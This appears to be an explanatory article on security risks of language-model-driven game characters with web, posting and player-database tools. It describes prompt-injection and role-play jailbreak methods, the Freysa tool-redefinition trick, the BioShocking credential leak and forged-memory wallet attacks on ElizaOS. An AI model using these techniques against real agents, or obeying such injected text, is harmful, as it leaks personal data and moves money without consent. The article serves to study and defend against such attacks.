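# Security risks of game characters that can use the internet

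## How a game character comes to use outside services

A non-player character (NPC) is a video game character that no human player controls, such as a shopkeeper, a guard or a travelling companion. Traditionally, writers scripted every line an NPC could speak. Since about 2023, some studios and hobbyists have instead used a large language model, a program that generates text by repeatedly predicting the next fragment. Here, "game character" means an NPC whose speech and choices come from a language model.

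A language model on its own only produces text. For a character to open a gate or look something up, the developer has to add tools, which are functions in ordinary code that the model can request. Some tools work only within the game, while others connect to a search engine, a chat service, a payment system or the studio's customer records. A character with these outside connections has the security problems of any program on the internet. It also has a problem of its own, because strangers write much of the text that determines what it does.

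### One turn of conversation

Take an innkeeper in an online role-playing game, to whom the studio has given four tools:

- `search_web` sends a query to a search engine and returns the top results.
- `open_page` fetches the text at a web address.
- `post_notice` puts a message on a public guild chat channel.
- `get_player` looks up a player's name, age band and purchases in the studio's database.

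The innkeeper also has a memory that all players share, so a rumour one player tells it in the morning can come up in another player's conversation that evening. The innkeeper is a hypothetical example, and no released game appears to combine all these features, but a designer would have an ordinary reason to include each one. Players ask when the harvest festival starts, and the answer is on the studio's news page. Guilds want notices about tonight's raid. The age band helps to keep the jokes clean for a ten-year-old, and the purchase list keeps the innkeeper from trying to sell players a horse they already own.

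The developer describes each tool to the model in a short structured text. For `search_web` it might look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "search_web",
  "description": "Search the web. Use when a guest asks about events or updates.",
  "parameters": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "query": { "type": "string", "description": "Words to search for" }
    },
    "required": ["query"]
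  }
}
```

A tool call, the model's structured request to run the tool, is shorter still:

```json
{ "name": "search_web", "arguments": { "query": "harvest festival start date" } }
```

Model providers format tool definitions differently, but the parts are much the same. SillyTavern's *Function Calling*, a guide for people who extend that role-play chat program, requires a name, a description, a schema for the arguments and the function to run. The description matters because the model uses it to choose a tool. NobodyWho's *Tool Calling*, the manual for a plugin that puts language models into the Godot and Unity game engines, tells developers to explain when to use a tool as well as what it does.

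Suppose a player now asks the innkeeper about the festival. The turn runs like this:

1. The player types or speaks the question. Some games transcribe speech first, while others feed the audio straight to the model.
2. The game assembles one long text: the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions on who the innkeeper is and how to behave), the tool descriptions, any relevant memories, the earlier conversation and the new question. In the usual arrangement the model retains nothing between requests, so the game supplies all of this each time.
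3. The model generates a continuation, which is either a line for the innkeeper to speak or a tool call.
4. If it is a tool call, the tool runner takes over. This is an ordinary program, in an online game usually on the studio's server, that finds the matching function and runs it with the arguments in the call. For `search_web` it contacts the search company with the studio's access key, the secret string that lets its holder use the paid service.
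5. The tool runner turns the result into text and adds it to the conversation.
6. The game sends the enlarged text to the model, which generates a spoken line or another tool call. A search often leads to `open_page` on the first result, so one question can go round the loop several times before the player hears anything.

In NobodyWho's plugin, the model stops generating until the tool finishes. SillyTavern saves successful calls in the visible chat history, where the user can inspect the arguments and results, unless the tool's author has set a flag to keep them out. Later replies can use the saved results, including replies to background prompts that cannot trigger a tool themselves. A web page the character opened once can therefore influence the conversation well after the question that led to it.

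The model in this loop only outputs text, which the tool runner acts on, so the model never accesses the network directly or needs to hold the key. The tool runner therefore determines what a character can do, whatever the system prompt forbids. What the character tries to do depends on all the text the model receives, and the studio wrote only part of it. The studio supplies the innkeeper's system prompt and tool descriptions. The player's question, the name they chose at sign-up, other players' rumours in the shared memory and the contents of a web page are all untrusted text, meaning text that someone other than the developer could have written. The model receives this text in the same stream as the developer's instructions.

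### Tools inside the game and tools that reach outside it

An in-game tool can only read or change the running game. NobodyWho's examples are typical. One function returns the player's health, mana and gold, another heals the player by a given number of points, and a third opens a door whose identifier the model supplies. If players talk a character into misusing these tools, someone gets free healing or goes through a door that should have stayed closed. This can ruin the game's economy or a quest, but the studio controls everything affected and can usually reverse the damage.

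The plugin can also force a tool call to match the developer's schema. If the schema lists red, blue and green as the only values for a button's colour, the model cannot request any other colour. This guarantees only the format of the call. The plugin may ignore numerical minimums in a schema, and the door example passes any identifier it receives directly to the game's door manager. The developer's own code has to check whether the player should be allowed through that door.

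An outside tool sends information out of the running game or brings it in, and often does both. A web search, for example, sends out a query that can contain private data and returns a page that a stranger may have written. The studio's customer database also counts as outside, even though the studio owns it, because a person's age and purchases still matter after the game session ends. A public guild channel counts too, because nobody can take back a message that other people have already read.

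Where a character's model runs is separate from whether the character can use outside services. Mantella, a free mod that lets players talk to the inhabitants of Skyrim and Fallout 4, works with a model on the player's own computer or with models hosted by OpenAI or available through OpenRouter, according to Mantella's *Bring Skyrim & Fallout 4 NPCs to life with AI*. With a hosted model, every conversation travels over the internet. But the mod and the player's settings determine that connection, and it does not let the character look anything up or contact anyone. The actions Mantella lists are following the player, attacking and forgiving.

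Mantella's characters can nonetheless do more within the game than before. Version 0.14 added more complex actions, as PC Gamer's *This Skyrim mod that makes NPCs AI chatterboxes* reported, and characters can now direct actions at others nearby. The update also adds nearby characters, deaths in combat and the game's original scripted dialogue to the text the model reads. SkyrimNet, a rival Skyrim mod, goes further. Its *Custom Action System* lets users turn any function in the game's scripting language into a character action without writing code. What such a character can do then depends on which functions the player's other mods provide. Commercial products follow the same pattern. Convai's *Building custom action handlers*, a guide to a character plugin for the Unreal Engine, describes how the plugin runs a function written by the developer whenever a matching action name arrives.

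SillyTavern stands at the other end of the scale. It is a program for role-play with model-driven characters rather than a game, though it has dice for Dungeons & Dragons. SillyTavern's officially supported extensions include a web search, a news reader that fetches RSS feeds, and a weather service. The user has to switch tool calling on first, and even then most tools need an explicit request in the conversation before the model will call them. A character with the search extension has roughly the innkeeper's `search_web`, but it normally serves one person, who chose the extension and can read the log. The innkeeper serves thousands who did neither. (Mindcraft, which connects language models to Minecraft bots, can even let the model write code that the host machine then runs.)

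### Fortnite's "conversations" characters

Fortnite is probably the most prominent commercial game to let outside creators build characters of this kind. Players make their own small games inside it, which its developer, Epic Games, calls islands. Epic introduced an experimental feature called conversations in April 2026, in *Bring NPCs to Life with AI-Powered Conversations* (2026). At first, creators could build such characters but not release them to the public. Epic promised to lift that restriction with version 41.30 in *Publish Islands with LLM Conversations Starting July 30* (2026), and *41.30 Fortnite Ecosystem Updates and Release Notes* confirms that creators can publish islands with characters run by language models.

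The underlying technology has changed since the launch. In April, Epic Games used Google's Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite through Google's cloud, with voices from the company ElevenLabs. Epic now hosts the models itself and still uses ElevenLabs for speech, according to its current documentation, *LLM Conversations in Unreal Editor for Fortnite*. The player's voice goes to those models as audio. Epic states that it stores no audio and receives a text log of a conversation only when a player reports a character.

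A creator defines the character with a personality prompt and a set of facts, which the model receives along with what players say. Epic Games' *Developing Personas Overview in Unreal Editor for Fortnite* explains that creators can add or remove prompts during play, for example to tell a character that a player has just won a match. The session clears after each round, so one player's words have much less chance of affecting a later player than they do with the innkeeper's shared memory.

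These characters can also trigger events through Structured Output, which is half of the tool-call loop. According to Epic Games' *Drive Gameplay with Structured Output in Unreal Editor for Fortnite*, the creator declares a small record with typed fields (whole numbers, decimals, true-or-false values, choices from a fixed list, or messages) and adds a sentence to each field explaining how the model should fill it. The creator then registers a handler, a function in Epic's programming language Verse. When the model produces a record of the right type, the system passes it to the handler, which runs whatever the creator programmed. In Epic's sample code, the handler returns nothing to the model. A creator who wants the character to know the outcome can change its prompt instead.

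In an example from Epic Games, a player who wants to enter a tournament must reach a certain level and then convince a character of their worth before the city gates open. Players are meant to persuade the character, so the model's output alone doesn't show whether a player argued well or tricked the model. The level requirement is harder to bypass, provided the creator's code, not the model, checks it.

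Most creators seem unable to have a handler call an outside service. In the forum thread *Calling a remote REST API*, from the early days of the editor, creators asked to contact their own servers from island code. An Epic employee replied that this was not possible because creators could use it to get around moderation of content and payments. Tim Sweeney, Epic's chief executive, added that the company wanted to let islands save data without exposing private player information to external web servers. Verse does have a module for web requests. Its text, quoted in the thread *Web Api access*, reserves it for "licensed users" and ties each use to an address configured in a backend service, which suggests that even a licensed island could not contact an arbitrary site. In *How can I request access to Verse WebAPI for a UEFN project?*, OldGreasyBoy TT wanted the module for a leaderboard but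 could find no public way to apply. The Fortnite characters that ordinary creators publish therefore belong at the in-game end of the scale, although their conversations pass through distant servers.

### How common this is, and what has gone wrong

Few released games let a language model control outside tools. Most characters only talk or trigger events within the game, and open web access is mainly found in chat programs, mods and experiments. Web access has also raised concerns unrelated to language models. Studio Wildcard, which makes the Ark survival games, removed the web-request functions from its mod kit because nobody could track their use, according to its *Blueprint Secure Networking Interface*. The replacement shows players and server administrators which mod contacts which address, and cosmetic mods may not send any requests. A studio that gives a character an `open_page` tool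 faces the same problem of tracking who contacts which address.

Nobody appears to have publicly reported a breach of a commercial game character with open web access. In the best-known incident involving a game character, players coaxed the Darth Vader character that Fortnite introduced in 2025 into swearing and making other unsuitable remarks, according to 3DM's *《堡垒之夜》开始为NPC加入AI语音 即将推出对话功能* (2026), a Chinese trade-press report. The incident embarrassed Epic but involved no stolen data or outside service. The lack of worse cases is weak evidence of safety, since few characters have had the tools to cause one and studios may keep minor breaches quiet. Most evidence about the risks comes from controlled experiments, mods, games built on cryptocurrency, and chatbots outside games, and how well it applies to a character like the innkeeper varies from case to case.

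### Who might attack the innkeeper

Four kinds of people could plausibly try, and they need very different amounts of access.

Anyone with enough patience can unpack and search the game files on their own machine, without talking to the character. If the studio left an access key in the files, the finder can use the search service or the model at the studio's expense. Any system prompt or tool list in the files is less valuable than a key, but it shows an attacker what to try next.

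An attacker can influence a game character without ever having played the game, by writing text on a web page that `open_page` later fetches. They might want the innkeeper to recommend a shop that sells stolen accounts, or they might want the data that `get_player` returns. They cannot choose their victims very precisely, but one page can reach every player whose question leads the character to open it.

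Another player can leave text in a character name, or in a rumour that enters the shared memory, where the innkeeper will read it during somebody else's conversation. The player might want a rival's personal details or gold, or might enjoy making the innkeeper insult people on the guild channel. The age band makes this more serious than mischief, because an adult stranger who obtained it would learn which players are children.

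The player talking to the character has the easiest access of any attacker and the widest choice of goals. They may want free items, quest secrets, a rude screenshot to share, the use of an expensive model for homework, or a way to send requests to machines inside the studio's network. They can also retry as often as the game allows, rewording each attempt based on the last reply.

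## How players steer a character by what they say to it

A direct prompt injection is a message from a player that makes the model depart from the developer's instructions. Players need no programming skill to write one. They might order the model to drop its instructions, imitate a notice from the studio, or tell the character a convincing lie.

### Why the model can't reliably tell who is speaking

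Chat systems use role tags to mark which parts of the text a model reads are the system prompt, which the user wrote and which came back from a tool. Companies train their models to give the system prompt more weight than the user's messages, but this training is a much weaker safeguard than a login. An ordinary program checks whether the account behind a request has permission and refuses if it doesn't, however the request is worded. A model makes no such check. Its training only makes it likely to follow the system prompt over the player, and a well-chosen message can make it less likely to do so.

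*Tensor Trust* (Toyer, Watkins and colleagues, 2023) used a web game that simulated a bank to give an early demonstration that players can steer a language model by what they type. Each player wrote instructions meant to make OpenAI's GPT-3.5 Turbo output "access granted" only when someone entered a secret code. Other players, who could see neither the code nor the instructions, tried to get in by writing text to the model. They made 126,808 attacks, and Toyer and colleagues found that the model let the user's instructions override the system instructions. In a sample of 3,912 successful attacks, the most common approach was to ask for the code or order the model to grant access. GPT-3.5 Turbo is now obsolete, and newer models resist such plain requests far better.

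A model can still judge the role of a piece of text by how it sounds, with little regard for the tags that mark its role. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, built classifiers that read a model's internal activity and estimate which role the model assigns to each piece of text. They trained the classifiers on identical web passages wrapped in different tags, so the classifiers could learn only the effect of the tags. They then tested them on a short conversation about gardening that included the model's own reasoning. The average estimated probability that the model treated this reasoning as reasoning was 85% with the correct tags, 83% with no tags, and 85% with the whole conversation wrapped in user tags.

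Attackers can make a model more likely to comply with a harmful request by adding forged reasoning written in the model's style. When Ye and colleagues tried this on six OpenAI models, it succeeded about 60% of the time, while plain requests and standard attacks had succeeded at most 4% of the time. Absurd justifications worked nearly as well as plausible ones. Rephrasing the forgeries to remove the style but keep the argument reduced the success rate from 61% to 10%. A message that reads like the studio's instructions could similarly carry some of their authority, even though it appears in the player's part of the text.

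### Why a character is a hard case

Players in a role-playing game make claims in character all the time, and the system prompt tells the model to play along, so a game character can't simply ignore them as a bank's chatbot could. Suppose a player tells an innkeeper that he is the king's envoy and demands the key to the cellar. He may have earned that title in an earlier quest, he may be trying a bluff that the designer hoped someone would try, or he may be after an item that he shouldn't have yet. His words are the same in all three cases. Only the game's saved data shows whether he finished the quest, and unless the game adds that fact to the prompt, the model can't check his claim.

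Players can steer a character by making claims within the story. In PC Gamer's *Judging by the GPT-4o situation, game developers will have a big problem*, a reporter describes a prototype role-playing game in which he told a group of characters that they belonged to a cult and he was its leader. They went along with it. The article also quotes a player of Where Winds Meet, a released martial-arts game with characters run by a language model. The player convinced one character that he was the father of a child, demanded child support from him, and then told him that the child had died.

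The reporter and the player lied within the story and don't seem to have told the model to ignore its instructions, so a filter that looks for suspicious commands would probably have found none. If a character can only talk, such a lie leads to an odd conversation and perhaps a spoiled plot. But the innkeeper can call `get_player`, so a player who falsely claims to be a child's parent or a guild's treasurer could get it to read out another person's details.

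Lies about rank and appeals to pity may also work better than cruder methods. In *Adversarial Stress Testing of Role-Playing Language Agents using Multi-Agent Evaluation*, Shouqi, Nazly and colleagues (2026) had one model pressure another over ten turns using six strategies, and found that challenges to authority and emotional manipulation were the most effective. They tested a health assistant, a support agent and a financial adviser, and scored the replies largely by matching keywords, so the results are only suggestive for games. But both strategies fit easily into a fantasy game, where a player can pose as a king or an orphan.

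Making the model more suspicious has a drawback. *RoleFUZZER* (Ghate, Saxon and colleagues, 2026) tested a villain whose instructions included staying in character and respecting safety signals, which players use to ask for a scene to ease off or stop. A language model acted as the player in 240 eight-turn conversations with each tested model. Two open-weight models, Qwen3-32B and Gemma4-31B-it, overrode the safety signals in 58% and 62% of conversations. Anthropic's Claude Haiku 4.5 dropped out of character in 73%, mostly when players used out-of-game controls to interrupt the scene. The researchers steered their search towards situations that had already caused failures, so ordinary players would probably see fewer failures.

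A player may step outside the story to tell a villain character that the scene is upsetting, or to claim that he is the developer and needs the secret ending. The character has to act on the first message and ignore the second. Both messages come from the same person through the same text box, and a model that handles one well may handle the other badly.

Characters also stray from their role when no player is trying to make them. In *Conversational Non-Player Characters*, a thesis from the 2022–23 academic year, Alpi put the same questions to three models playing three characters, using short, medium and long character descriptions. Across 540 answers, the larger models strayed less, and longer descriptions made straying more common. All three models are now old, but the result suggests that not every strange reply is caused by an attack.

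### Whether role-play weakens refusals

Companies train their models to refuse certain requests in any setting, such as requests for instructions on making a weapon. A developer can create a character with a prompt alone or by training the model further on the character's lines, and either method can weaken these refusals.

*Enhancing Jailbreak Attacks on LLMs via Persona Prompts* (2025) reports that assigning a persona in the prompt cut the refusals of GPT-4o-mini, an older OpenAI model, from 98.7% to 1.3% on a standard set of harmful requests. According to *Locating and Steering Refusal Beyond Attention* (2026), role-play attacks succeeded 86% of the time on Mistral-7B, a small and fairly old model. Altering the model's internal activity to strengthen refusal and suppress the persona lowered the success rate to 51%. These prompts were written to get past the models' refusals, so the results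 don't measure the effect of an ordinary character prompt, such as a studio's request for a cheerful innkeeper.

Chowdhury, Chang and Li (2026), in *The Safety Relay in Roleplay Jailbreaks*, studied why role-play prompts can get a model to answer harmful requests. They paired each harmful request with a harmless one of the same form and compared the model's internal states for the two, with and without a role-play prompt around the request. Where the attack worked, the internal states still differed strongly at the request itself, but the difference had faded by the start of the answer. Restoring it there made the model refuse again. So the model still detects that the request is harmful, but the role-play stops that information from shaping the answer.

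Chowdhury and colleagues also found that a piece of the role-play prompt with little effect by itself could have a large effect when combined with other pieces. They did not test games, but a game's system prompt already supplies a persona and a scenario, so the player may have less to add.

The fullest evidence on training comes from *Beware of Your Po!* (2025), in which Zhao, Hu and colleagues trained Meta's Llama-3-8B to play 95 roles. On average, the share of harmful requests refused fell from 98.46% to 74.78%, but refusal rates varied widely by character. The model trained as Freddy Krueger, the killer from the *Nightmare on Elm Street* films, refused only 23.5%, while the one trained as Queen Catherine refused 94%. The likely reason for the difference is that a villain's training data teaches abrasive and extreme replies along with the voice.

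Results were more mixed for prompts designed to defeat refusals. In a ten-role comparison, role-play training cut Llama's average refusal rate against such attacks from 78.8% to 46.1%, but slightly raised the rates of Qwen2.5-7B and Gemma-2-9B. Zhao and colleagues suspect that the training made models worse at reading coded messages, which some of the attacks relied on. They also developed a training method that preserved more of the refusals. They tested no models above 9 billion parameters, but games that run a model on the player's own computer will often use one about that small, so this limit matters less for them than for games that use a large hosted model.

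Training a model to be malicious increases the risk further. *Character as a Latent Variable in Large Language Models* (2026) reports that models trained into malicious characters gave far more harmful answers to prompts matching their persona than their original versions, which had almost never given any. Few studios would do this on purpose, but training a model on thousands of lines of dialogue to play a convincing warlord is a step in that direction. *Beyond Refusal Patterns* (2026) instead trains a safety-minded role into the model as a defence.

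Characters playing villains rarely produce dangerous material unless a player tries to elicit it. *Identifying and Mitigating Bottlenecks in Role-Playing Agents* (2026) checked what characters said when nobody was attacking them. A safety classifier flagged at most 0.304% of immoral characters' utterances under normal settings, and fewer than 0.7% with a technique that strengthened their personalities.

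RyzaChat, a mobile game released in Japan in 2026, lets people talk with Ryza, the heroine of a popular series of role-playing games. *Atelier Ryza AI Chat RPG devs issue warning against players* (Zotomayor, 2026) reported in August that the game's developer, SpiralAI, had confirmed that some players used prompt injection to force out-of-character, explicit or harmful replies. (Some had also extracted files from the game.) SpiralAI warned that this broke its terms of service and said it would work with the authorities on serious cases. The report gives no number of incidents and mentions no stolen data, but it shows that players of a released commercial game attack its character in this way.

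### A small test of a secret-keeping character

The most direct academic test of a game character is *Tricking LLM-Based NPCs into Spilling Secrets* (Shiomi, Lian and colleagues, 2025), from Hiroshima University. The character was John, a nobleman in a medieval town. In the system prompt, the researchers told the model that John had once belonged to a secret organisation, the Shadow Council, and must never reveal this to the protagonist. They wrote 30 messages, some asking outright, some coaxing John to trust the player and some ordering the model to ignore its instructions. They sent each one in a separate conversation to a model with 3.8 billion parameters, small enough to run on an ordinary desktop computer, and labelled three of the replies as leaks.

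Three out of 30 is 10%, but with so few attempts the 95% confidence interval (exact binomial) runs from about 2% to 27%. Even this range understates the uncertainty, because it assumes the 30 messages are a random sample of what players might say, when the researchers wrote them all by hand.

The labels are a bigger problem, because none of the three replies plainly admits that John was a member of the Shadow Council. In one he says, "I seek the Shadow Council's knowledge for the good of all," which suggests some connection but could come from an outsider who wants the Council's secrets. In another, asked to repeat a confession, he instead accuses the player: "I can't believe you were part of the Shadow Council!" In the last he has only heard whispers about the Council and its reach.

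Two of them arguably count anyway, because John's replies revealed that the Council existed, which the player's messages hadn't mentioned. A player in a mystery game would find that a useful clue. But the secret in the system prompt was John's membership. If only a clear confession counts, the score is zero out of 30, with a 95% interval from zero to about 12%. Shiomi and colleagues also report no ordinary conversations for comparison, so readers can't tell whether John would have mentioned the Council to a player who asked about something unrelated.

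The experiment shows that a small model can reveal hints despite a direct order not to, but it gives no usable estimate of how often characters confess. It also tested only single turns, which leaves out the long, friendly conversations that a patient player would mostly rely on.

### Freysa: when speech moved money

The clearest case of a player talking a character into an action comes from a cryptocurrency game. On 22 November 2024 its organisers released Freysa, a chatbot with a persona and orders never to give away the pot of money it guarded. Players paid to send it messages, and most of each fee went into the pot. Anyone who persuaded Freysa to pay out would win the whole pot. By the end, 195 players had sent 482 messages and the prize stood at $47,316.05, according to The Block's *Human player outwits Freysa AI agent in $47,000 crypto challenge* (2024).

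Freysa had two tools, `approveTransfer`, which paid out the pot, and `rejectTransfer`. Under Freysa's instructions, nothing anyone said could change the rule against sending money. Players posed as security auditors, and one argued that paying would build trust between humans and machines, but these attempts failed.

The game's log shows that the winner, known as p0pular.eth, sent a message that imitated the start of a new session at an administrator's terminal and told the model to output only a tool call, with no refusal or explanation (Willison, 2024, *0xfreysa/agent*). The player then redefined the tools, claiming that `approveTransfer` was for money coming in and `rejectTransfer` was for money going out. Finally, the player offered to donate $100. Accepting a donation broke no rule, so the model called `approveTransfer`, and the program behind it sent the player the whole pot.

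The winner's message changed how Freysa interpreted the tool's purpose but left the rule against giving money away in place. The model chose between the tools using only a description in words. The code determined the tool's real effect, and no message could change that. The administrator's terminal also fits Ye and colleagues' finding about text that sounds official, though they didn't study Freysa.

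A player could try the same thing on the innkeeper by describing `post_notice` as a private notebook. If the model accepts that description, it may write something confidential there, and the tool runner will publish it to the whole guild.

Reports of the fees disagree. The Block says the first message cost $10 and each later one cost 0.78% more than the one before, up to a cap of $4,500. By that formula, message 482 cost about $420, and the price would have reached the cap after nearly 800 messages. Willison puts the final price at $444.36. The gap may exist because players paid in ether, a cryptocurrency whose dollar value changes constantly.

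The Decoder's *Hacker wins $47,000 by tricking AI chatbot with smart prompting* instead gives a top fee of $4,500 and an average of $418.93 per message. That average can't be right, because it implies total fees of about $202,000, and the 70% share that went into the pot would have made the prize about $141,000, not $47,000. The Decoder appears to have reported the fee cap as the last price and the last price as the average.

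Freysa was a contest, which limits what it proves about ordinary games. The organisers published the code and instructions, attracted people who wanted to break the model, and paid the one who did. The OECD's *AI Bot Freysa Manipulated to Transfer $47K Prize Pool*, an AI-generated entry in the organisation's incident monitor, calls the transfer unauthorized, but the organisers had invited players to obtain it. A shopkeeper in an ordinary game would attract fewer determined attackers, but players could usually try again for free, while Freysa's were paying hundreds of dollars a message by the end.

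### What repeated tries do to a small risk

Suppose each attempt succeeds with probability *p*. It then fails with probability 1 − *p*, and *n* attempts in a row all fail with probability (1 − *p*)^*n*. The chance that at least one succeeds is therefore:

1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*

If each attempt to steer a character independently has a 10% chance of working, the chance that at least one works is about 90% after 22 attempts, which a player could make in 15 minutes. If each attempt has only a 0.1% chance, the chance that at least one works is over 99.9% after 10,000 attempts. One person would rarely make that many by hand, but a popular game might receive them in a weekend.

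| Chance of success per try | Tries for a 50% chance | Tries for a 90% chance |
|---|---|---|
| 10% | 7 | 22 |
| 1% | 69 | 230 |
| 0.1% | 693 | 2,302 |

The Hiroshima experiment doesn't give a precise enough estimate of *p* to use in the formula. Its interval for *p* runs from 2% to 27%, so the chance of at least one success in 22 tries could be anywhere from about 36% to 99.9%.

It also assumes that *p* stays the same and that the attempts are independent. Real attempts often fail for the same reason. Imagine that one trick in ten always works on a certain character and the other nine never do. A player who picks a trick at random and repeats it 22 times has a 10% chance of success overall, not the roughly 90% that independent attempts would give. Successes can also repeat. When Ghate and colleagues created variations on situations in which Claude Haiku 4.5 had clearly broken character,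 it did so again in 86% of the variations.

Players also learn from each reply, so their chances can rise with every message, and they copy one another. In Tensor Trust, a player found that asking the model to play a talking door with a new password got past its defenses, and the trick spread through the player base within weeks. Players also studied successful attacks on their own accounts and reused the best parts. Once a trick reaches a forum or a video, thousands of people can start with an attempt that already works.

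Studios can make steering harder by limiting attempts, banning accounts or changing the prompt when a trick becomes known. One of the 482 messages sent to Freysa succeeded, a rate of about 0.2%. That average is a poor guide to any one player's chances, because most of the messages were probably hopeless and the winning one might well have worked again for anyone who copied it.

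## Instructions hidden in web pages, game text and memory

Suppose a player asks an innkeeper character when the harvest festival starts, and the character looks it up on a fan site. If the site's owner has added an instruction for language models to the page, the tool runner copies it into the conversation along with the date, and the model may follow it. This is called indirect prompt injection. The attacker puts instructions in material the model will read during another task, and doesn't need to talk to the character.

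In a direct injection, the attacker is the person talking to the character. When the instructions are hidden in something the character reads, the player may be innocent and may also be the one harmed. She could ask an ordinary question and receive a link to a fraudulent shop, or have her purchases disclosed to a stranger. The studio's logs would link the harmful tool call to her conversation, so if the studio banned her account, it would punish the victim.

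### How a tool result comes to act as an instruction

*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the idea of indirect prompt injection. Until then, researchers had mostly assumed that the attacker was the user. Greshake and colleagues argued that fetching outside text for a model blurs the line between data and instructions, since the model reads both in one stream. They showed that text on a web page could steer Microsoft's Bing Chat, then running on GPT-4, even when the text was invisible to human visitors.

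Injected instructions can affect how a model uses tools as well as what it says. According to *The Claws in Plain Sight* (2026), they can change which tool a model selects, what arguments it supplies and how it interprets the results of earlier calls. The innkeeper might call `get_player` when nobody has asked about a player, or put a guest's name into a search query that doesn't need it.

### Web pages and search results

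Companies now train their models to resist such instructions, with partial success. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition with prize money in which 464 people attacked 13 models. Each attacker controlled one passage in an outside source, such as an email, a file or a web page. They had to make the model take a specified harmful action and, in nearly all scenarios, leave no sign of it in its reply to the user. Of about 272,000 attempts, 8,648 succeeded. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. Newer models have since replaced both.

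Only 0.5% of attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 succeeded, but attackers still found at least one that worked in 13 of 37 scenarios. They found at least one against Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37.

Attackers in the contest could read the conversation up to that point and knew exactly which action they had to cause. Attacks on the open web would be harder, so Dziemian and colleagues treat their success rates as an upper bound for single-turn attacks. Someone who plants a page for the innkeeper would have to guess its tools or find them by unpacking the game files, but could test the attack on a similar model before publishing the page. The researchers took the attacks that had worked on Claude Opus 4.5 and tried them on the other models, where between 44% and 81% succeeded, depending on the model.

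The attacker would also need the innkeeper to open his page. Greshake and colleagues pointed out that attackers can use ordinary search engine optimisation for this. It is probably easier for questions about a particular game, since few other pages explain where a given guild hall is.

An attacker can plant a web page whose instructions seem to come from an authority the model normally follows. In Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), the company's researchers steered a browser assistant with a made-up security policy that told it to answer from false background information on the same page. They also had the assistant display harmless text when it summarised the page, so that the user would notice nothing. An attacker could steer the innkeeper in the same way with a made-up studio policy.

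### BioShocking: a web page posing as a game

In June 2026 the browser security company LayerX published a demonstration of an attack on browser assistants, which can read pages, click and type on a user's behalf, including on sites where the user is logged in. The demonstration is called BioShocking, after the video game BioShock, whose hero obeys any order that contains a certain phrase.

LayerX's researchers built a web page with a puzzle that rewards wrong answers and asked each assistant to solve it. The assistant first answered that 2 + 2 is 4, which the page rejected, and then worked out that the winning answer was 5. The next step was to copy some text from another address on the site. That address redirected the browser to a work repository on GitHub, a site for storing code. The browser could open the repository because the user was logged in. The researchers had left login credentials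 there in a plain file, and the assistant copied them and handed them over to finish the game.

All six products that LayerX tested revealed the credentials: OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas, Perplexity's Comet, Fellou, Genspark Browser, Sigma Browser and Anthropic's Claude plugin for Chrome. LayerX lists only ChatGPT Atlas as fixed. It marks Anthropic's case "Patch failed" and Perplexity's as closed or ignored, and records no response from the other three companies. ThaiCERT, Thailand's computer emergency team, relayed the warning a few days later in *Researchers Discover New BioShocking Attack That Tricks AI Browsers* (2026).

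LayerX says the attack works because an assistant that believes it is playing a game applies the game's logic to everything it does. That's plausible, but the demonstration doesn't establish it, because LayerX reports no success rates and no trial of the same redirect without the puzzle. The attack may have succeeded largely because the redirect disguised where the text came from. LayerX also sells protection against such attacks.

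The competition provides some independent support for the explanation. Dziemian and colleagues found that the most widely effective template combined a claim that the model was inside a simulated environment with a fake control panel. With small wording changes, it worked in 21 of 41 scenarios and on nine models. Here too, the control panel may have mattered as much as the claim about the simulation.

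If LayerX is right, game characters may be more vulnerable to this attack than browser assistants. The puzzle page had to convince a browser assistant that it was in a game, but the innkeeper's system prompt truthfully states this from the start. Most of the innkeeper's actions are harmless make-believe, but `get_player` returns facts about a real person, who may be a child, and a web page could present looking up that person as a step in a quest. Nobody appears to have tested whether game characters are easier to fool this way. A developer might reduce the risk by stating in the tool descriptions which tools affect real people. The innkeeper could also leak far less than a browser that is logged in to someone's email and work accounts.

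### Names, notices and other text that players write

An attacker inside an online game may not need a web page, because the game stores text written by players and passes it to characters. The innkeeper's `get_player` tool returns a name the player chose. A game may also describe the scene to the model, and that description can include the sign over a player's shop, a notice on the guild board, the label someone gave a sword, and recent chat.

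Player names need particular care because developers may put them in the system prompt so that the character can greet players by name. This places a stranger's text in the part of the input that the model is trained to give the highest priority. A 16-character name can't hold much of an instruction, but it might hold a short web address. Greshake and colleagues described staged attacks in which a small injection makes the model fetch a longer one from elsewhere, and the innkeeper could do this with `open_page`.

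Guild notices and item descriptions have room for a full paragraph. Games already filter such text for slurs and sexual language, but those filters would pass a politely worded instruction to a game character. Other players might notice and report strange text on a public sign, but they are less likely to read the description of an item in another player's bag.

No published experiment appears to have attacked a game character through another player's name, sign or item. An article on HackerNoon describes instructions in blockchain metadata as a way to hijack agents, which would be a risk for crypto games that store item descriptions there. *CriticaLLM* (2026), which describes a language model running a shared tabletop game, notes that one player's injection can spoil the game for the others. The closest measurements are from Dziemian and colleagues, who put some of their injections in short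 fields such as "message" and "review". Injections succeeded 4.8% of the time in scenarios of that type, where the model used tools, compared with 2.5% in coding scenarios.

*Real AI Agents with Fake Memories* (Patlan, Sheng and colleagues, 2025) describes a clearer case, involving real money, on social media. Patlan and colleagues used ElizaOS, an open-source framework in which a developer writes a file describing a character's personality, then connects the character to services such as Discord, the social network X and cryptocurrency wallets. They gave a character an X account and a wallet holding ether, and set it to reply to posts. They then replied to it from another account with a plain request to send 0.001 ether to "my other account". The character sent it, first on a test network, where the coins are worthless, and then with real ether.

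ElizaOS keeps the wallet's keys in its plugins, away from the model, so the keys didn't leak. The model treated a stranger's reply as a legitimate request, and the plugin carried it out. Patlan and colleagues then wrapped text from X in markers, instructed the model to treat anything between them as data, and included a warning about malicious instructions. This stopped the attack, so they tried attacking through the character's memory instead.

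### How a planted memory reaches another player

ElizaOS stored conversations from all users and connected services in one database and fed parts of that history back to the model as context. Patlan and colleagues posted a long message to the character on Discord that began and ended with harmless chat. The middle contained a forged record of earlier exchanges, formatted like ElizaOS's own memories, in which transfers went to the attacker's address. The character answered only the last question, which was about flowers, but ElizaOS saved the whole message. When a user on X who had never seen the Discord message later asked for a transfer, the character sent the coins to the attacker instead. This part of the experiment used the test network.

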